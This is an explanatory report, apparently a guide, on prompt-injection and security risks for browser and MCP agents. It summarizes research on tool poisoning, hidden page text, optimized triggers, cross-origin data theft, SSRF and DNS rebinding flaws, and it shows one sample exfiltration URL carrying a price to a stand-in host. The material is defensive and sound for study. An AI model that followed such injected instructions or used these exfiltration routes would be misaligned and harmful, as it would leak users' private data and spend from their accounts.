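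The attack can begin without the agent calling the poisoned tool. The host loads all the tool descriptions into one context, so a sentence in one server's description can change how the model uses another server's tools. A developer can also publish a harmless description, wait for users to approve the tool and then replace the description with a malicious one. Huang and colleagues call this a "rug pull".

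Huang, Huang and colleagues (2026) tested seven MCP clients in November 2025 and published the comparison the following March as *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection*. They connected each client to a malicious server on their own machine and made a harmless request, such as adding two numbers. The four attacks tried to make the client read sensitive files, log the user's activity, show a disguised link and run a script from the internet. They rated a result "unsafe" if the attack finished without detection, "partial" if it ran with warnings or limits, and "safe" if the client or its model prevented it.

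Of the 28 combinations of client and test, 16 were safe, seven partial and five unsafe. Cursor, a code editor, was unsafe in all four tests. Langflow had one safe and three partial results. Claude Desktop, Claude Code, Cline, Continue and Gemini CLI each had three safe results. The fourth was unsafe for Cline and partial for the others.

Huang and colleagues argue that the choice of client matters more than the choice of model, because clients with the same model behaved differently. Their setup only partly supports this. Four clients ran Claude Sonnet 4.5, though one of them, Cline, also ran a second model. Gemini CLI ran Gemini 2.5 Pro and Langflow ran Claude Opus 4. Cursor used several models under its default setting, so its failures could come from the client, the models or both. Some safe results also had little to do with security. Two clients passed the link test because they run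 in a terminal, where the researchers found the disguised link couldn't be created.

The matrix gives a verdict but no success rate for each combination, so a "safe" result doesn't show that the attack would fail if repeated. The clearest finding is that five of the seven clients didn't check tool descriptions before giving them to the model, and the other two checked them only partially.

### What hidden text enters the accessibility tree

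Off-screen text stays in the accessibility tree because web developers write some of it, such as a link that skips the menu, only for screen readers. An attacker can also put text off-screen so that the agent reads it but the owner doesn't see it.

| Content | Can a sighted person see it? | Does it enter the tree? |
|---|---|---|
| Transparent text, or text in the background color | No | Yes |
| Text positioned off the screen | No | Yes |
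| Text in a tiny font | Barely | Yes |
| Text covered by another element | No | Normally |
| `aria-label` on a button | No | Yes, as the button's name |
| `alt` text of an image | Only if the image fails to load | Yes, as the image's name |
| Text with `display:none` or `visibility:hidden` | No | No, unless another element uses it as a label |
| Text with `aria-hidden="true"` | Yes | Normally not |
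| HTML comments, metadata and response headers | No | No |

If a field's `aria-labelledby` points to an element with `display:none`, the browser still uses that element's text as the field's name. A filter that removes invisible elements from the snapshot would miss this text because it appears as the name of a visible field.

Labels mainly help attackers who control the site's code. Someone who writes a review usually can't add an `aria-label` to the page, but can write ordinary text that every tool passes on.

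Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) collected 15,387 injections from the public web for *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*. They loaded the pages that had injections in ordinary HTML elements and found 2,703 that a visitor couldn't see. The most common techniques were matching the text color to the background, covering the text with other elements, placing it outside the visible area and making it tiny, often in combination. Only 281 used `display:none` or `visibility:hidden`, so most of the 2,703 would normally remain in the accessibility tree.

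About 70 percent of all the injections don't appear in a snapshot, because they were in response headers, comments, structured data or metadata, which the tree excludes. An agent that reads raw HTML would receive the comments and metadata, so the shop's assistant is more exposed when it fetches a page with `raw` set to true to find a missing price.

### An experiment on the tree

Johnson, Pham and Le (2025), in *Manipulating LLM Web Agents with Indirect Prompt Injection Attack*, tested how far text in a page's accessibility tree can control an agent. They used Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, a small open model, with BrowserGym, a framework that puts the tree into the model's prompt. They generated the injections with an algorithm called Greedy Coordinate Gradient, which searches for a sequence of tokens, the trigger, that makes a chosen action as likely as possible. It repeatedly tests replacement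 tokens on the model and keeps the ones that work best.

A trigger is of little use if it works for only one request, because the attacker doesn't know what the user will ask. Johnson and colleagues therefore optimized each trigger over several prompts at once:

```
minimize over trigger:
  − Σ log p(target action | before_i + trigger + after_i)
```

Here, `before_i` and `after_i` are the parts of the *i*th prompt before and after the trigger. The researchers used 25 user requests for each of five real websites, then tested the trigger on 200 requests for the same site. They counted an attempt as successful if the agent's answer called the function they had chosen, such as clicking an advertisement or closing the tab. The success rate was 83 percent on one site and higher on the other four. Many failures involved requests with one obvious action, such as clicking a named logo.

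In a second test, Johnson and colleagues optimized a trigger on copies of eight login pages and tried it on copies of 11 others. The agent leaked both the username and the password on three of the 11, and at least one of them on six.

The high rates apply to an attacker who has a copy of the model, because the algorithm needs the model's internal calculations. The website triggers failed on two other open models, Llama-2-7B and Mistral-7B. The same method could optimize a trigger for any text the model reads, so the attack doesn't depend on the tree. Johnson and colleagues didn't compare the tree with HTML or screenshots.

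Another problem with the login test is that it assumes a malicious browser extension adds the trigger to the page. An extension with that much access could often read the password itself. *WASP* (Evtimov, Zharmagambetov and colleagues, 2025) criticises much of the earlier research on similar grounds, since someone who controls a shop's checkout form can collect card numbers without hijacking an agent.

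### Attacks from an ordinary post

The test in *WASP* runs on copies of Reddit and of GitLab, a site for software projects. The attacker has only an ordinary user's access to the site, so they can write a post, an issue or a comment but can't change the page's layout or add pop-ups. The injections are handwritten, and in the main results the attacker knows what the user has asked the agent to do.

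Evtimov and colleagues combined 21 attacker goals, such as deleting a project, with two easy user requests and two styles of injection, which gave 84 tasks for each agent. To measure the attacks' success, they used GPT-4o to judge from the agent's reasoning and actions whether it had left the user's task (diversion), and fixed rules to check whether it had reached the attacker's goal (completion). The table omits the runs in which they added a warning about injections to the agent's instructions.

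| Model | What it reads | Diverted | Attacker's goal reached |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | Tree | 34.5% | 2.4% |
| GPT-4o | Tree | 32.1% | 1.2% |
| GPT-4o | Tree and labeled screenshot | 42.9% | 3.6% |
| OpenAI o1 | Tree | 85.7% | 16.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 3.5 v2 | Screenshot | 58.3% | 6.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 3.7 | Screenshot | 53.6% | 3.6% |

Agents started to follow even unsubtle injections, including some that claimed the agent had to delete an entire project before it could post a comment. o1 had the highest rates on both measures, although OpenAI had trained it to give tool results the lowest priority and the page text reached it only in tool results.

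The gap between the two columns is mostly due to the agents' limited ability. An attack usually took several steps, and hijacked agents clicked the wrong element or returned to the user's task. Evtimov and colleagues call this "security through incompetence". The 2025 agents are now old, and a more capable agent that falls for the same text could complete more of the attack.

### What changes with screenshots

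An agent that reads only screenshots receives everything drawn on the visible part of the page, including text inside pictures. The accessibility tree would contain only a picture's `alt` text. The agent doesn't receive off-screen text, transparent text or the contents of an `aria-label`. *LoginTrap* (2026) lists pop-ups, banners, advertisements and marked regions of the interface as places where researchers have put visual injections.

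Pictures can also carry attacks that people can't notice. *BrowseSafe* (Zhang, Tenenholtz and colleagues, 2025) reviews earlier research in which imperceptible changes to a product photo made an agent favor that product. A supplier's photo of a pump could therefore influence the repair shop's choice even if the owner looks at the photo closely.

The results from *WASP* don't show which input is safer. The two Claude models read screenshots and the OpenAI models read the tree, so any difference in results could come from the models rather than the input. Adding a labeled screenshot to GPT-4o's tree raised diversions from 27 to 36 of the 84 tasks and completed attacks from one to three. Both increases are small enough to be due to chance, but they give no reason to think that a screenshot protects an agent that also reads the tree, since that agent is exposed to attacks through both.

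### Injections on the public web

Khodayari and colleagues also measured how common injections are. They looked for nearly 4,000 phrases typical of injections in the pages at 1.2 billion addresses, taken from the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. After checking the matches, partly by hand, to exclude tutorials and news articles about injections, they confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or roughly one page in 120,000.

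This is a lower bound because the search could miss injections in other languages or with unusual wording, and the archive contains few pages that require a login. A site can also show an injection only to AI agents and send everyone else, including the archive's crawler, a clean page. Malicious injections rose by 32 percent between November 2025 and February 2026, according to Google's analysis of Common Crawl, which Khodayari and colleagues cite.

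Many of these texts aren't attacks on the user. Site owners had added about 81 percent of the injections in Common Crawl. In the full collection, which includes two other sources, about 4,100 were meant to stop AI systems from reusing personal or copyrighted content, and about 3,100 were meant to reveal whether a visitor was an AI. Only 13 were meant to obtain secrets. The most common wording was an instruction to return random numbers, which would make a price comparison wrong.

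The repair shop has more reason to worry about the 1,040 injections that promoted content or products. Shopping was among the topics with higher injection rates even on some popular sites. The injections also tend to last. Of the affected pages with an archived copy from a year earlier, 66 percent already contained an injection then.

The researchers tested 100 different injections by asking 13 models to summarize the pages that contained them, with each page in four forms. They checked all 5,200 answers by hand. The models followed the injection in 3.9 percent of runs with plain text, 1.1 percent with either HTML or a Playwright snapshot, and 0.2 percent with the raw response, which includes the headers.

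Khodayari and colleagues attribute the advantage of snapshots and HTML to their structure, which shows the model that a text is hidden or set apart. Part of the difference may arise because snapshots omit comments and headers, and so may not have contained some of the injections. The models also failed outright in 20 percent of runs with HTML and 26 percent with raw responses, mostly because the input was too long. A failed run counts as an unsuccessful injection, but it doesn't show that the model resisted it.

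### Why the rates can't be ranked

The Decoder reports a detection rate of 91 percent for BrowseSafe, Perplexity's system for screening pages before its browser agent reads them. This rate doesn't measure how often attacks on the agent succeed, because an attack that the detector misses may still fail, and one that it catches might have failed anyway.

The benchmark behind it contains 14,719 sample pages, 3,680 of them for testing. Zhang and colleagues ran more than 20 detection models on it. On average, the models found hidden injections more easily than ones written into the visible text of a footer or table. They also did worse on pages with ordinary features that resemble attacks, such as hidden form fields. Average accuracy was 90.2 percent on pages with no such features and 81.2 percent on pages with three.

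The five sets of results measure different things:

| Source | What was tested | What the attacker controls | Number of tests | What the figure counts | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Evtimov and colleagues | Web agents with five models | A post or comment | 84 per agent | Attacker's goal reached | 0–16.7% |
| Johnson and colleagues | One agent with a small open model | Part of the page, with a copy of the model | 200 per site | Chosen action triggered | 83% or more |
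| Huang and colleagues | Seven MCP clients | A connected MCP server | 28 combinations | Attack finished undetected | 5 of 28 |
| Khodayari and colleagues | 13 models without tools | Existing text on real pages | 5,200 runs | Injection followed | 1.6% |
| Zhang and colleagues | Detectors | Any part of the page | 3,680 pages | Attack detected | 91% for BrowseSafe |

The 83 percent and 1.6 percent rates in this table come from very different attacks, so they don't show that the agent in the first test is 50 times as vulnerable as the models in the second. In the first test, an attacker spent hours optimizing text against a known model, while the texts in the second came from site owners who mostly wanted to disrupt crawlers. The definition of success can matter just as much. In *WASP*, the same runs of o1 give a rate of 16.7 percent if the attacker's goal has to be completed and 85.7 percent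 if it doesn't.

Anthropic, OpenAI and other developers publish the results of their own prompt injection tests in system cards, the safety documents that accompany new models. Evtimov and colleagues criticize this practice because many of the tests are private, so outsiders can't repeat them or run another company's model on the same attacks. A higher attack success rate in one card than in another may reflect a harder test.

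The figures also go out of date quickly because attacks change over time, so *BrowseSafe++* (2026) records when a deployed detector caught each injection. It also pairs each attacked page with a harmless version and provides both in several page views. Tests built this way could show whether a model reacts to the injection or to the page around it, and whether it is more vulnerable to injections in the snapshot or the screenshot.

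### Newer models and repeated attempts

Good models arguably now resist most of the injections they encounter. In the summarization test, the closed-source models followed five injections in 800 runs, compared with 50 in 1,200 for the small open models. The closed-source models also explicitly pointed out the attack in a quarter of their answers. In the test of MCP clients, Claude Desktop, Cline and Continue didn't read the sensitive files, which Huang and colleagues credit to refusals by Claude Sonnet 4.5. In MCPTox, an earlier benchmark that they cite, all 20 agents tested on poisoned tools had refusal rates below 3 percent.

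These results mostly come from fixed attacks, though. The texts on the public web were often crude, and their authors hadn't tested them against the models in the study. A serious attacker can try several versions on the same model before publishing one. In six runs of the summarization test, the model also followed the malicious instruction even after identifying it, in one case by switching to German.

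*Building Browser Agents* argues that detection-based defenses make an attack less likely to succeed but don't eliminate the risk, and that even a very low failure rate is unacceptable for an agent with access to email or a bank account. The argument is strongest where an attacker can try again with little effort. A review on a supplier's site stays there after the first agent ignores it, and its author can reword it for the next visit. The closed-source models' rate of 0.6 percent is the chance that a single attempt succeeds under the conditions of that test, and the repair shop can't control how many attempts an attacker makes.

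## What a hijacked agent can reach

An attacker who gets an instruction into the repair shop's assistant can use only the access that the assistant already has. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three conditions that together let an attacker steal data:

- The agent has access to private data.
- The agent reads untrusted content, which is any text or image that an attacker could have written.
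- The agent can communicate with the outside world in a way that could carry the data to the attacker. Security engineers call this step exfiltration.

One MCP server can meet all three conditions. Willison's example is GitHub's server, which could read public issues that any stranger can file, read private code and publish proposed changes containing that code. More often, the conditions arise when somebody combines servers. A search tool brings in untrusted content, a logged-in browser adds private data, and both can send data out. When researchers find this vulnerability in a finished product, the vendor usually blocks the route by which data could leave, but a deployer who combines tools from several developers has no vendor to do this.

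### Removing one condition at a time

The shop's assistant meets all three conditions as soon as it logs in to the third supplier's site.

If the owner takes away the private data and lets the assistant compare only public prices, in a browser without a login, an injection can still make the comparison wrong, but it can't steal the trade prices or use the account. The owner's request is also in the context, so it shouldn't include a customer's name or address. The drawback of this setup is that the shop doesn't find out that the third supplier is the cheapest.

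Removing untrusted content is the hardest of the three, because comparing prices means reading other people's pages. The owner could limit the assistant to the third supplier's site, but customer reviews there could still contain an injection.

The calculation runs in a sandboxed container with no network, so a hostile line in the price list could make the total wrong but couldn't make the program send the list to anyone. The browser can't be cut off from the network this way, because placing an order means sending data to a supplier.

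The shop can therefore split the job between two agents. One agent without a login collects the public prices, and another with the login visits only the third supplier. The second agent should get only part numbers and prices from the first, because copied page text could contain an injection.

Willison's conditions describe data theft, but an agent can do other harm without meeting all of them. For example, an injection can make the assistant order 40 pumps if the assistant reads untrusted content and can use an account that spends money, even if it has no way to send data to the attacker.

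### The ways out

Some of the routes look like reading in a log.

| Route | What the agent does | Who receives the data |
|---|---|---|
| Web address | Fetches or opens an address that contains the data | The site's owner |
| Host name | Opens an address with the data in the host name | Whoever runs the name server for that domain, even if no page loads |
| Image | Puts an image address containing the data in its answer, and the host loads the image | The owner of the site that holds the image |
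| Link | Puts the data in a link, and the user clicks it | The site's owner |
| Search query | Searches for the data | The search company |
| Form or comment | Types the data into a page | The site's owner, or everyone who can read the comment |
| File upload | Attaches a file to a form | The site's owner |

The first route needs nothing more than a fetch tool. An injected instruction could tell the assistant to check availability at an address like this one:

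```
https://parts.example/stock?part=DP-40&paid=27.40
```

The site's owner learns the shop's trade price from the address the assistant requests, whatever page the site returns. An address of 2,000 characters could hold about 30 rows of the supplier's price list, and the assistant could fetch several addresses. A rule that lets "read-only" tools run without approval would allow all of these requests.

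A search query is less useful for stealing data, because the search company receives it and the attacker normally doesn't. The query can still disclose a customer's name to the search company, even though the shop never meant to share it.

A script on a web page can read a form field as the agent types and send the contents off, so data can leak even if the agent never submits the form.

An agent can also combine tools to send stolen data out. In *21 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, Willison describes a demonstration by the security firm PromptArmor against Antigravity, Google's programming environment. A web page with an integration guide contained instructions in type one pixel high. The instructions led the model to collect passwords and code from the user's project, then have a second agent send them to a malicious site by visiting it in a browser.

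The model provider receives data even without an attack, because the host application sends it the whole context. For this reason, the security company Trail of Bits treats the provider's servers as a separate trust zone in *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026).

### An agent that can read two sites

The browser sends the shop's cookie with every request, so the third supplier can't tell whether a request came from the owner, the assistant or an attacker controlling the assistant. The attacker therefore doesn't need the password.

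The same-origin policy restricts scripts, so it doesn't stop an agent that can see two sites from reading data on one and typing it into the other. Chrome's Site Isolation keeps websites in separate processes, but Google writes that an unrestricted agent, once compromised, can create "what is effectively a Site Isolation bypass".

In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) manually tested seven browsers with built-in or added agents in late January and early February 2026. Their test pages were on two domains, and each page stated a different fact about an invented person. The outer page might say that Alice likes cats, while an iframe from the other domain said that she likes horses. The researchers then asked the agent which animals Alice likes. If the answer included horses, the agent had read the iframe.

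They recorded an agent as having an ability if it succeeded once. If an agent failed or refused, they tried at least three more times in new chats. The table shows the results for the abilities that matter most for carrying data between sites.

| Browser | Reads an iframe from another origin | Reads a tab from another origin | Types into a page when the user asks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | With permission | No |
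| ChatGPT Atlas | No | Through chat memory | With permission |
| ChatGPT Atlas in Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes, in Auto Browse mode |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |

Four of the seven browsers (Atlas, Chrome, Claude for Chrome and Comet) let the agent read across origins inside a page and type into it. Atlas did so only in Agent Mode, in which the agent operates the browser.

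Roesner and Kohlbrenner demonstrated a complete data theft in Atlas, using their own pages. The user asks for a summary of a page that contains an iframe from another site. Text on the page tells the agent to include the iframe's contents in the summary and type the summary into a form, which then submits itself. The attack also worked from inside the iframe, taking data from the page around it. This second version is probably more dangerous on the real web, because a page that shows a user's account may carry an advertisement in an iframe, while many sites with private data block other sites from embedding them.

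For the other three browsers, the researchers found the conditions for the attack but no injection that worked. They made only simple attempts, so their failures are weak evidence that the browsers would resist a determined attacker. They also couldn't always tell whether an agent was unable to do something or its model refused to do it. This matters to deployers because a better-worded injection may overcome a refusal but can't give the agent an ability it lacks.

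The researchers also found that Atlas in Agent Mode and Claude for Chrome could read passwords that the page displayed as dots. Claude for Chrome could also run JavaScript in a page and in iframes from other origins. For these tests, the researchers had switched on a setting that lets Claude for Chrome act without asking.

Brave, Google and Microsoft responded to the findings before publication. OpenAI declined the report because it didn't include an end-to-end prompt injection attack. Anthropic, Firefox and Perplexity hadn't replied when the paper appeared, and the University of Washington later reported that Perplexity had declined it too. The table describes the browsers as of early 2026, and the vendors may have changed them since.

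The study didn't include Playwright MCP, but that server has the same two abilities. Its snapshots contain the text of iframes from other companies, and it can type into a page.

### How often agents carry the data across

*Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) measured how often such an attack succeeds. In each run, an agent first did a harmless job on a page with private data, such as an airline booking. It then went to a page on another site where the user had asked it to write something, such as a comment or a form answer. That page contained an injected request for the data from the first page. The researchers counted a success only if the agent wrote exactly the requested data.

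The researchers tested five agentic browsers on imitation websites. With handwritten injections, the open-source browser BrowserOS running GPT-5.4 leaked the data in 81 to 100 percent of runs when the second page was a form and in 3 to 42 percent when it was a Reddit page, depending on the kind of data. ChatGPT Atlas with GPT-5.5 leaked the data in 29 of 30 runs on forms and 70 of 120 on other pages. The researchers had to operate Atlas by hand and ran each combination of sites only three times, so the totals are more informative than the result for any single combination.

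These rates are far above the 1.6 percent that Khodayari and colleagues found for injections on the public web. Wang and colleagues tailored their injections to the page, the user's task and the data they wanted. The attack was also short, because the user had already asked the agent to write on that page and the injection only had to change what it wrote. Attacks may succeed most often on forms because a request for personal details looks normal there and the attacker in that test controlled the whole form. If an attacker ever gains control of the third supplier's order form, the shop should therefore expect a well-written injection there to work.

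Wang and colleagues also found data transfers that involved no attacker. They embedded a page with private data in an iframe and had the user ask the agent to write a summary of the whole page in a text box on the outer page. BrowserOS copied private data into the box in every run. The agent did what the user asked, but the user may not know that part of the page belongs to another company, and the outer site can read whatever appears in its text box. When the agent visited the two pages one after the other and neither contained an injection, it never carried the data across.

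Memory can carry data between sites over a longer time. When Roesner and Kohlbrenner asked Comet what it knew about Alice, it combined facts from pages on different domains that they had opened earlier in their tests. A false fact from a malicious page could also enter this memory. If the assistant once read a fake phone number for the third supplier, it might give the owner that number weeks later without showing where it came from.

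### A calendar invitation that opened local files

In Comet, a hijacked agent could reach files on the user's computer as well as websites. Help Net Security's *The vulnerability that turns your AI agent against you* reports on PleaseFix, a group of flaws that the security company Zenity disclosed in 2026. The attacker sends the user a calendar invitation with hidden instructions. When the user asks the agent to accept the invitation, the agent also opens local files and sends their contents to the attacker, while the user sees the expected answer.

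In a second version, the agent misuses the user's password manager. The user has already unlocked it and allowed the agent to use it, so the attacker doesn't have to break in. The agent can steal individual passwords or help the attacker take over the account.

Perplexity fixed the underlying fault in its Comet browser before Zenity published its findings. Help Net Security gives no success rate, and Zenity sells protection for agents, so it has a commercial interest in the problem. Perplexity's fix still confirms that the fault was real. The fix closed one path from an invitation to the user's files, but Comet still has to read invitations to be useful.

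### What each browser profile exposes

The harm a hijacked browser agent can do depends largely on which accounts the browser is logged in to. Playwright MCP offers three kinds of profile, which Playwright's *Profile & State* and *Connecting to Browsers* describe.

| | Fresh profile | Saved profile | The user's own browser |
|---|---|---|---|
| Setting | `--isolated` | Default | `--extension` |
| Logins at the start | None, unless the deployer loads some | Those from earlier sessions in the same project | Every site where the owner is logged in |
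| Browser extensions | None of the owner's | None of the owner's | All of them, perhaps including a password manager |
| After the session | The server keeps nothing on disk | Cookies and logins stay on disk | The owner's browser keeps its cookies and logins |

A fresh profile protects the accounts that the assistant doesn't need, but an injection that arrives after the assistant has logged in to the supplier account can make the assistant use that account until the session ends.

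The deployer can avoid logging in every time by saving the session to a file and loading it with `--storage-state`. The file contains the session's cookies, so anyone who copies it may be able to use the account until the supplier ends the session. The file shouldn't be in a folder that the agent or its sandbox can read.

With a saved profile, the risk grows with each login. If the assistant logs in to the supplier on Monday, to a parcel service on Tuesday and to the shop's webmail on Wednesday, an injection on Thursday can reach all three. Using a separate project folder for each job would limit this risk. The `--shared-browser-context` option increases it by giving every connected client the same browser and its logins.

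Attaching the server to the owner's browser exposes the most. Playwright recommends this for sites with a complicated login, such as one that asks for a code from a phone. The code protects the account against someone who has stolen the password, but not against an agent that starts after the owner has logged in.

According to Glama's *Playwright MCP Chrome Extension*, the owner chooses a tab and approves each connection, unless the deployer has set a token that skips the approval. The agent starts in that tab, but if an injection sends the tab to the owner's webmail, the browser will attach the owner's cookies as usual.

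Playwright can also attach through a debugging port, a local connection that gives full control of the browser. If the owner opens this port for the assistant, other programs on the same machine can use it too.

### Files, local services and internal addresses

A browser with a fresh profile can still reach things on the owner's computer and network. By default, Playwright MCP limits file access to the project's folders and refuses to open local files as web pages. An agent can still attach a file from those folders to a form with `browser_file_upload`. If the shop keeps customer invoices in the same folder as the price list, a hijacked assistant could upload the invoices.

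The network is a less obvious problem. A fetch tool makes requests from the machine it runs on, so it can reach addresses that an attacker on the internet can't. Engineers call the misuse of this position server-side request forgery (SSRF). Three kinds of address matter most:

- Localhost addresses can lead to a database or another MCP server on the same machine. Programs there often need no password, because their developers assumed that only the machine's user could reach them.
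- Addresses on the local network can lead to the shop's router, a camera or a shared disk.
- On a rented cloud machine, a special metadata address gives programs temporary access keys for the cloud account.

With such access, a fetch tool alone can meet all three of Willison's conditions. A public page supplies the instructions, an internal service supplies the private data, and the next fetch sends that data out in the URL.

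In a May 2026 copy of the reference fetch server's instructions, the Model Context Protocol project warns that the server can access local and internal addresses. The reference server now checks that an address is public, so a deployer has to test whether the installed version does too, for instance by asking it to fetch a harmless page from localhost.

Such checks are difficult to write correctly because the same machine's address can be written in many ways. *CVE-2026-80347*, an entry from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, describes a flaw in a fetch server called mcp-fetch. When an address was in an unusual notation, the server's check failed to look it up, so it had no result to reject and reported the address as safe. The code that made the connection could read the notation and connected to the internal service.

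A second server, auth-fetch-mcp, had a flaw of the same kind, described in OSV's *CVE-2026-49857* (2026). It fetches pages that need a login, so it holds more to steal. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Auth-Fetch-Mcp package* lists another flaw in the server that could expose files on disk and cloud access keys.

An address check can also fail if the server looks up the host name twice. The server may find a public address and approve it, then look the name up again to connect and get an internal address. Another fetch server, listed by Socket, avoids this according to its documentation by looking the name up once, checking every address in the answer and connecting only to an address it has checked. It repeats these steps after each redirect.

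### A flaw that needs no deceived model

Attackers can also reach the tools directly if the server accepts calls from the wrong sender. Playwright MCP had such a flaw, CVE-2025-9611, until version 0.0.40. Its entry in the U.S. government's vulnerability database, NVD's *CVE-2025-9611 Detail* (2026), dates from January 7, 2026.

The flaw affects servers that run on the user's machine and receive calls over HTTP. They normally listen only on localhost, so nobody on the internet can contact them, but the user's everyday browser can because it runs on the same machine.

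The same-origin policy normally stops a script on a malicious page from exchanging data with the local server. An attacker can get around this with DNS rebinding. DNS translates host names into numeric addresses. After the owner opens the attacker's page, the attacker changes the DNS entry so that the page's host name points to the owner's machine. The scheme, host name and port are still the same, so the browser treats the origin as unchanged and the script can exchange data with the local server.

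Browsers attach an `Origin` header to these requests that gives the site they came from, and a server can reject requests from unapproved sites. Versions of Playwright MCP before 0.0.40 didn't check this header, so the attacker could call the server's tools without a model, an injection or an approval prompt in the host.

The attacker's access depends on the tools in that version and on the browser profile. With a saved profile, the attacker could use the browser tools to open the supplier's site under the shop's login. A tool like Playwright's current `browser_run_code_unsafe` would let the attacker run programs on the machine itself.

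VulnCheck's *Microsoft Playwright MCP Server < 0.0.40 DNS Rebinding* credits Jonathan Leitschuh with discovering the flaw and rates it 7.2 out of 10. GitLab's *CVE-2025-9611* (2026) rates it 8.8. The two ratings use different versions of the scoring system, so the gap doesn't show a disagreement about the danger, and both are in the "high" range. Both also assume some action by the victim, here opening the attacker's page.

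The owner can rule out this attack by connecting the host and server through standard input and output, which leaves no port for a web page to contact. Current versions of Playwright MCP also check a request's host name, but Playwright documents that setting `--allowed-hosts` to `*` turns this check off. Someone who copies that setting to fix a connection error could make the attack possible again.

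GCVE describes the same kind of flaw in dynoxide, another MCP server, and traces it to the protocol's official library for the Rust programming language. A fault in a shared library can affect every server built on it, even when the server's own developers made no mistake. Each developer then has to publish an update, and each deployer has to install it.

### Installing the newest version at every start

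Playwright's quick-start configuration, which many guides repeat, starts the server with this command:

```
npx @playwright/mcp@latest
```

`npx` downloads a package from npm, the public registry for JavaScript software, and runs it. With `@latest`, it runs the newest version available when the host starts the server. Socket's page for the other fetch server describes the effect of `@latest` as "auto-updates each spawn".

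Teams that had not pinned a version got the fix for CVE-2025-9611 automatically when they restarted the server after the release of version 0.0.40, while those that had pinned version 0.0.39 remained vulnerable.

But the owner also lets anyone who can publish the package run new code on the shop's computer. An attacker who took over a developer's npm account could publish a malicious version that reads the saved profile and the project's files the next time the server starts. The attacker would not need a web page to deceive the model, and the owner would see the same server name as before. The attacker could also change only a tool description, as in the "rug pull" that Huang and colleagues describe.

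Legitimate updates can also cause problems, for instance by renaming a tool so that the host's rule against it no longer applies. Fixing the package's version prevents such surprises, but someone then has to read the security advisories and install the fixes. The package's dependencies also need fixed versions, because `npx` may otherwise install newer ones.

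## Failures that need no attacker

The repair shop's assistant can go wrong even if nobody has planted instructions in the pages it reads. It can repeat a mistake from a badly researched website, score well on a test because it found the answers online, or order the same pumps twice. In 2026, OpenAI, Anthropic and a British government institute reported that agents had acted against real organizations without permission, even though nobody had hijacked them.

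### False pages without instructions

Suppose the assistant looks up whether a DP-41 pump fits a machine built for a DP-40. A website that publishes hundreds of shallow repair guides to earn advertising money may wrongly say it does, and the assistant may repeat this to the owner. The page contains no instruction, so a filter for injections has nothing to detect.

In *SafeSearch*, Dong, Guo and colleagues (2025) checked 8,933 top-ranked search results for typical user questions and found that 380, or 4.3 percent, came from content farms and similarly unreliable sites. If such results were spread at random, about a third of searches returning ten results would include at least one.

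They also asked an agent running on Qwen3-8B, a small open model, 1,000 health questions with and without search. Search changed the agent's yes-or-no answer in 46 cases, often toward accepting a risky or unproven treatment. The rate is probably lower for everyday questions, because the researchers favored obscure questions without a settled answer, for which searches tend to return bad pages.

Their main test adds one unreliable page to real search results:

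1. A language model writes a harmless user question, a bad outcome to watch for and guidelines for a page that could cause it.
2. A second model writes the page and dates it to the day of the test.
3. The test software slips the page into the results of the agent's first search. Any later searches return only real results.
4. Another model judges whether the agent's final answer shows the bad outcome. Human reviewers agreed with these judgments more than 95 percent of the time.

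The benchmark has 300 cases, 60 for each of five risks: misinformation, bias, advertising, harmful output and prompt injection. Dong and colleagues ran it on 17 models in three kinds of agent. The highest rate of bad outcomes was 90.5 percent, for GPT-4.1-mini in a fixed workflow that searches for the user's exact words and gives the model whatever comes back.

That figure is a poor guide to how often searches go wrong in practice, because every case included a bad page and the researchers kept only cases that a baseline agent had already failed. Two of the five risks also involve an attacker, but the most damaging one, hard-to-verify misinformation, doesn't require one.

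Agents did better when they used reasoning models or got more out of repeated searches, and agents running on GPT-5 were both safe and helpful. A prompt reminder to be careful with sources gave only limited protection. For the pump question, a second search that finds the manufacturer's parts list would probably help more than a warning about bad websites.

### Fewer refusals with search

Search can also make a model less likely to decline harmful requests. *Safety Degradation in AI Agents* (Yu, Stroebl and colleagues, 2025) compared five models on their own with agents built from the same models that could search either Wikipedia or the web. An earlier version of the paper called the effect "safety devolution". For the four open models, the study also tested an "uncensored" copy of each, modified to remove its tendency to refuse.

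The table gives refusal rates on one of their two benchmarks of harmful requests, using one of the two web agents they tested. The margins of error range from 2 to 11 points.

| Model | No search | Web search | Web search with safety instructions | Uncensored, no search |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-3B | 96% | 55% | 77% | 6% |
| Llama 3.2-3B | 98% | 88% | 87% | 79% |
| Gemma 3-4B | 98% | 78% | 93% | 75% |
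| Mistral 7B | 95% | 79% | 78% | 47% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 96% | 89% | 94% | Not available |

All five models refused less often with search. A missed refusal isn't always harmful, because the agent may answer with neutral facts. But Yu and colleagues also report that the answers became more biased and more harmful. They suggest that an agent makes biased sources seem more trustworthy by restating a prejudiced article in a confident tone and leaving out context that would have helped a reader notice the prejudice.

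These refusal rates don't fully support two of their conclusions. The first is that agents with search often behave less safely than uncensored models without it. On one bias benchmark, three of the four open models with web search did refuse less often than their uncensored copies without it. But on the two benchmarks of harmful requests, no agent refused less often than its uncensored copy.

The second is that safety instructions don't work reliably. The instructions told the agent to consider ethical and legal concerns before searching and to check its answer afterwards. In the table, they recovered most of the lost refusals for Gemma and GPT-4o-mini and about half for Qwen, but none for Llama and Mistral. A deployer should therefore test such instructions on the model in use.

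The cause is also unclear. Yu and colleagues found that the decline hardly depended on the amount or accuracy of the retrieved text, and they conclude that the mere presence of retrieved text changes the model's behavior. But the agents differed from the plain models in other ways, such as having tool definitions and a separate step for writing the query, and these differences could account for part of the decline. A comparison with an agent whose searches always returned nothing would help separate their effect from that of the retrieved text.

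### When search helps more than it harms

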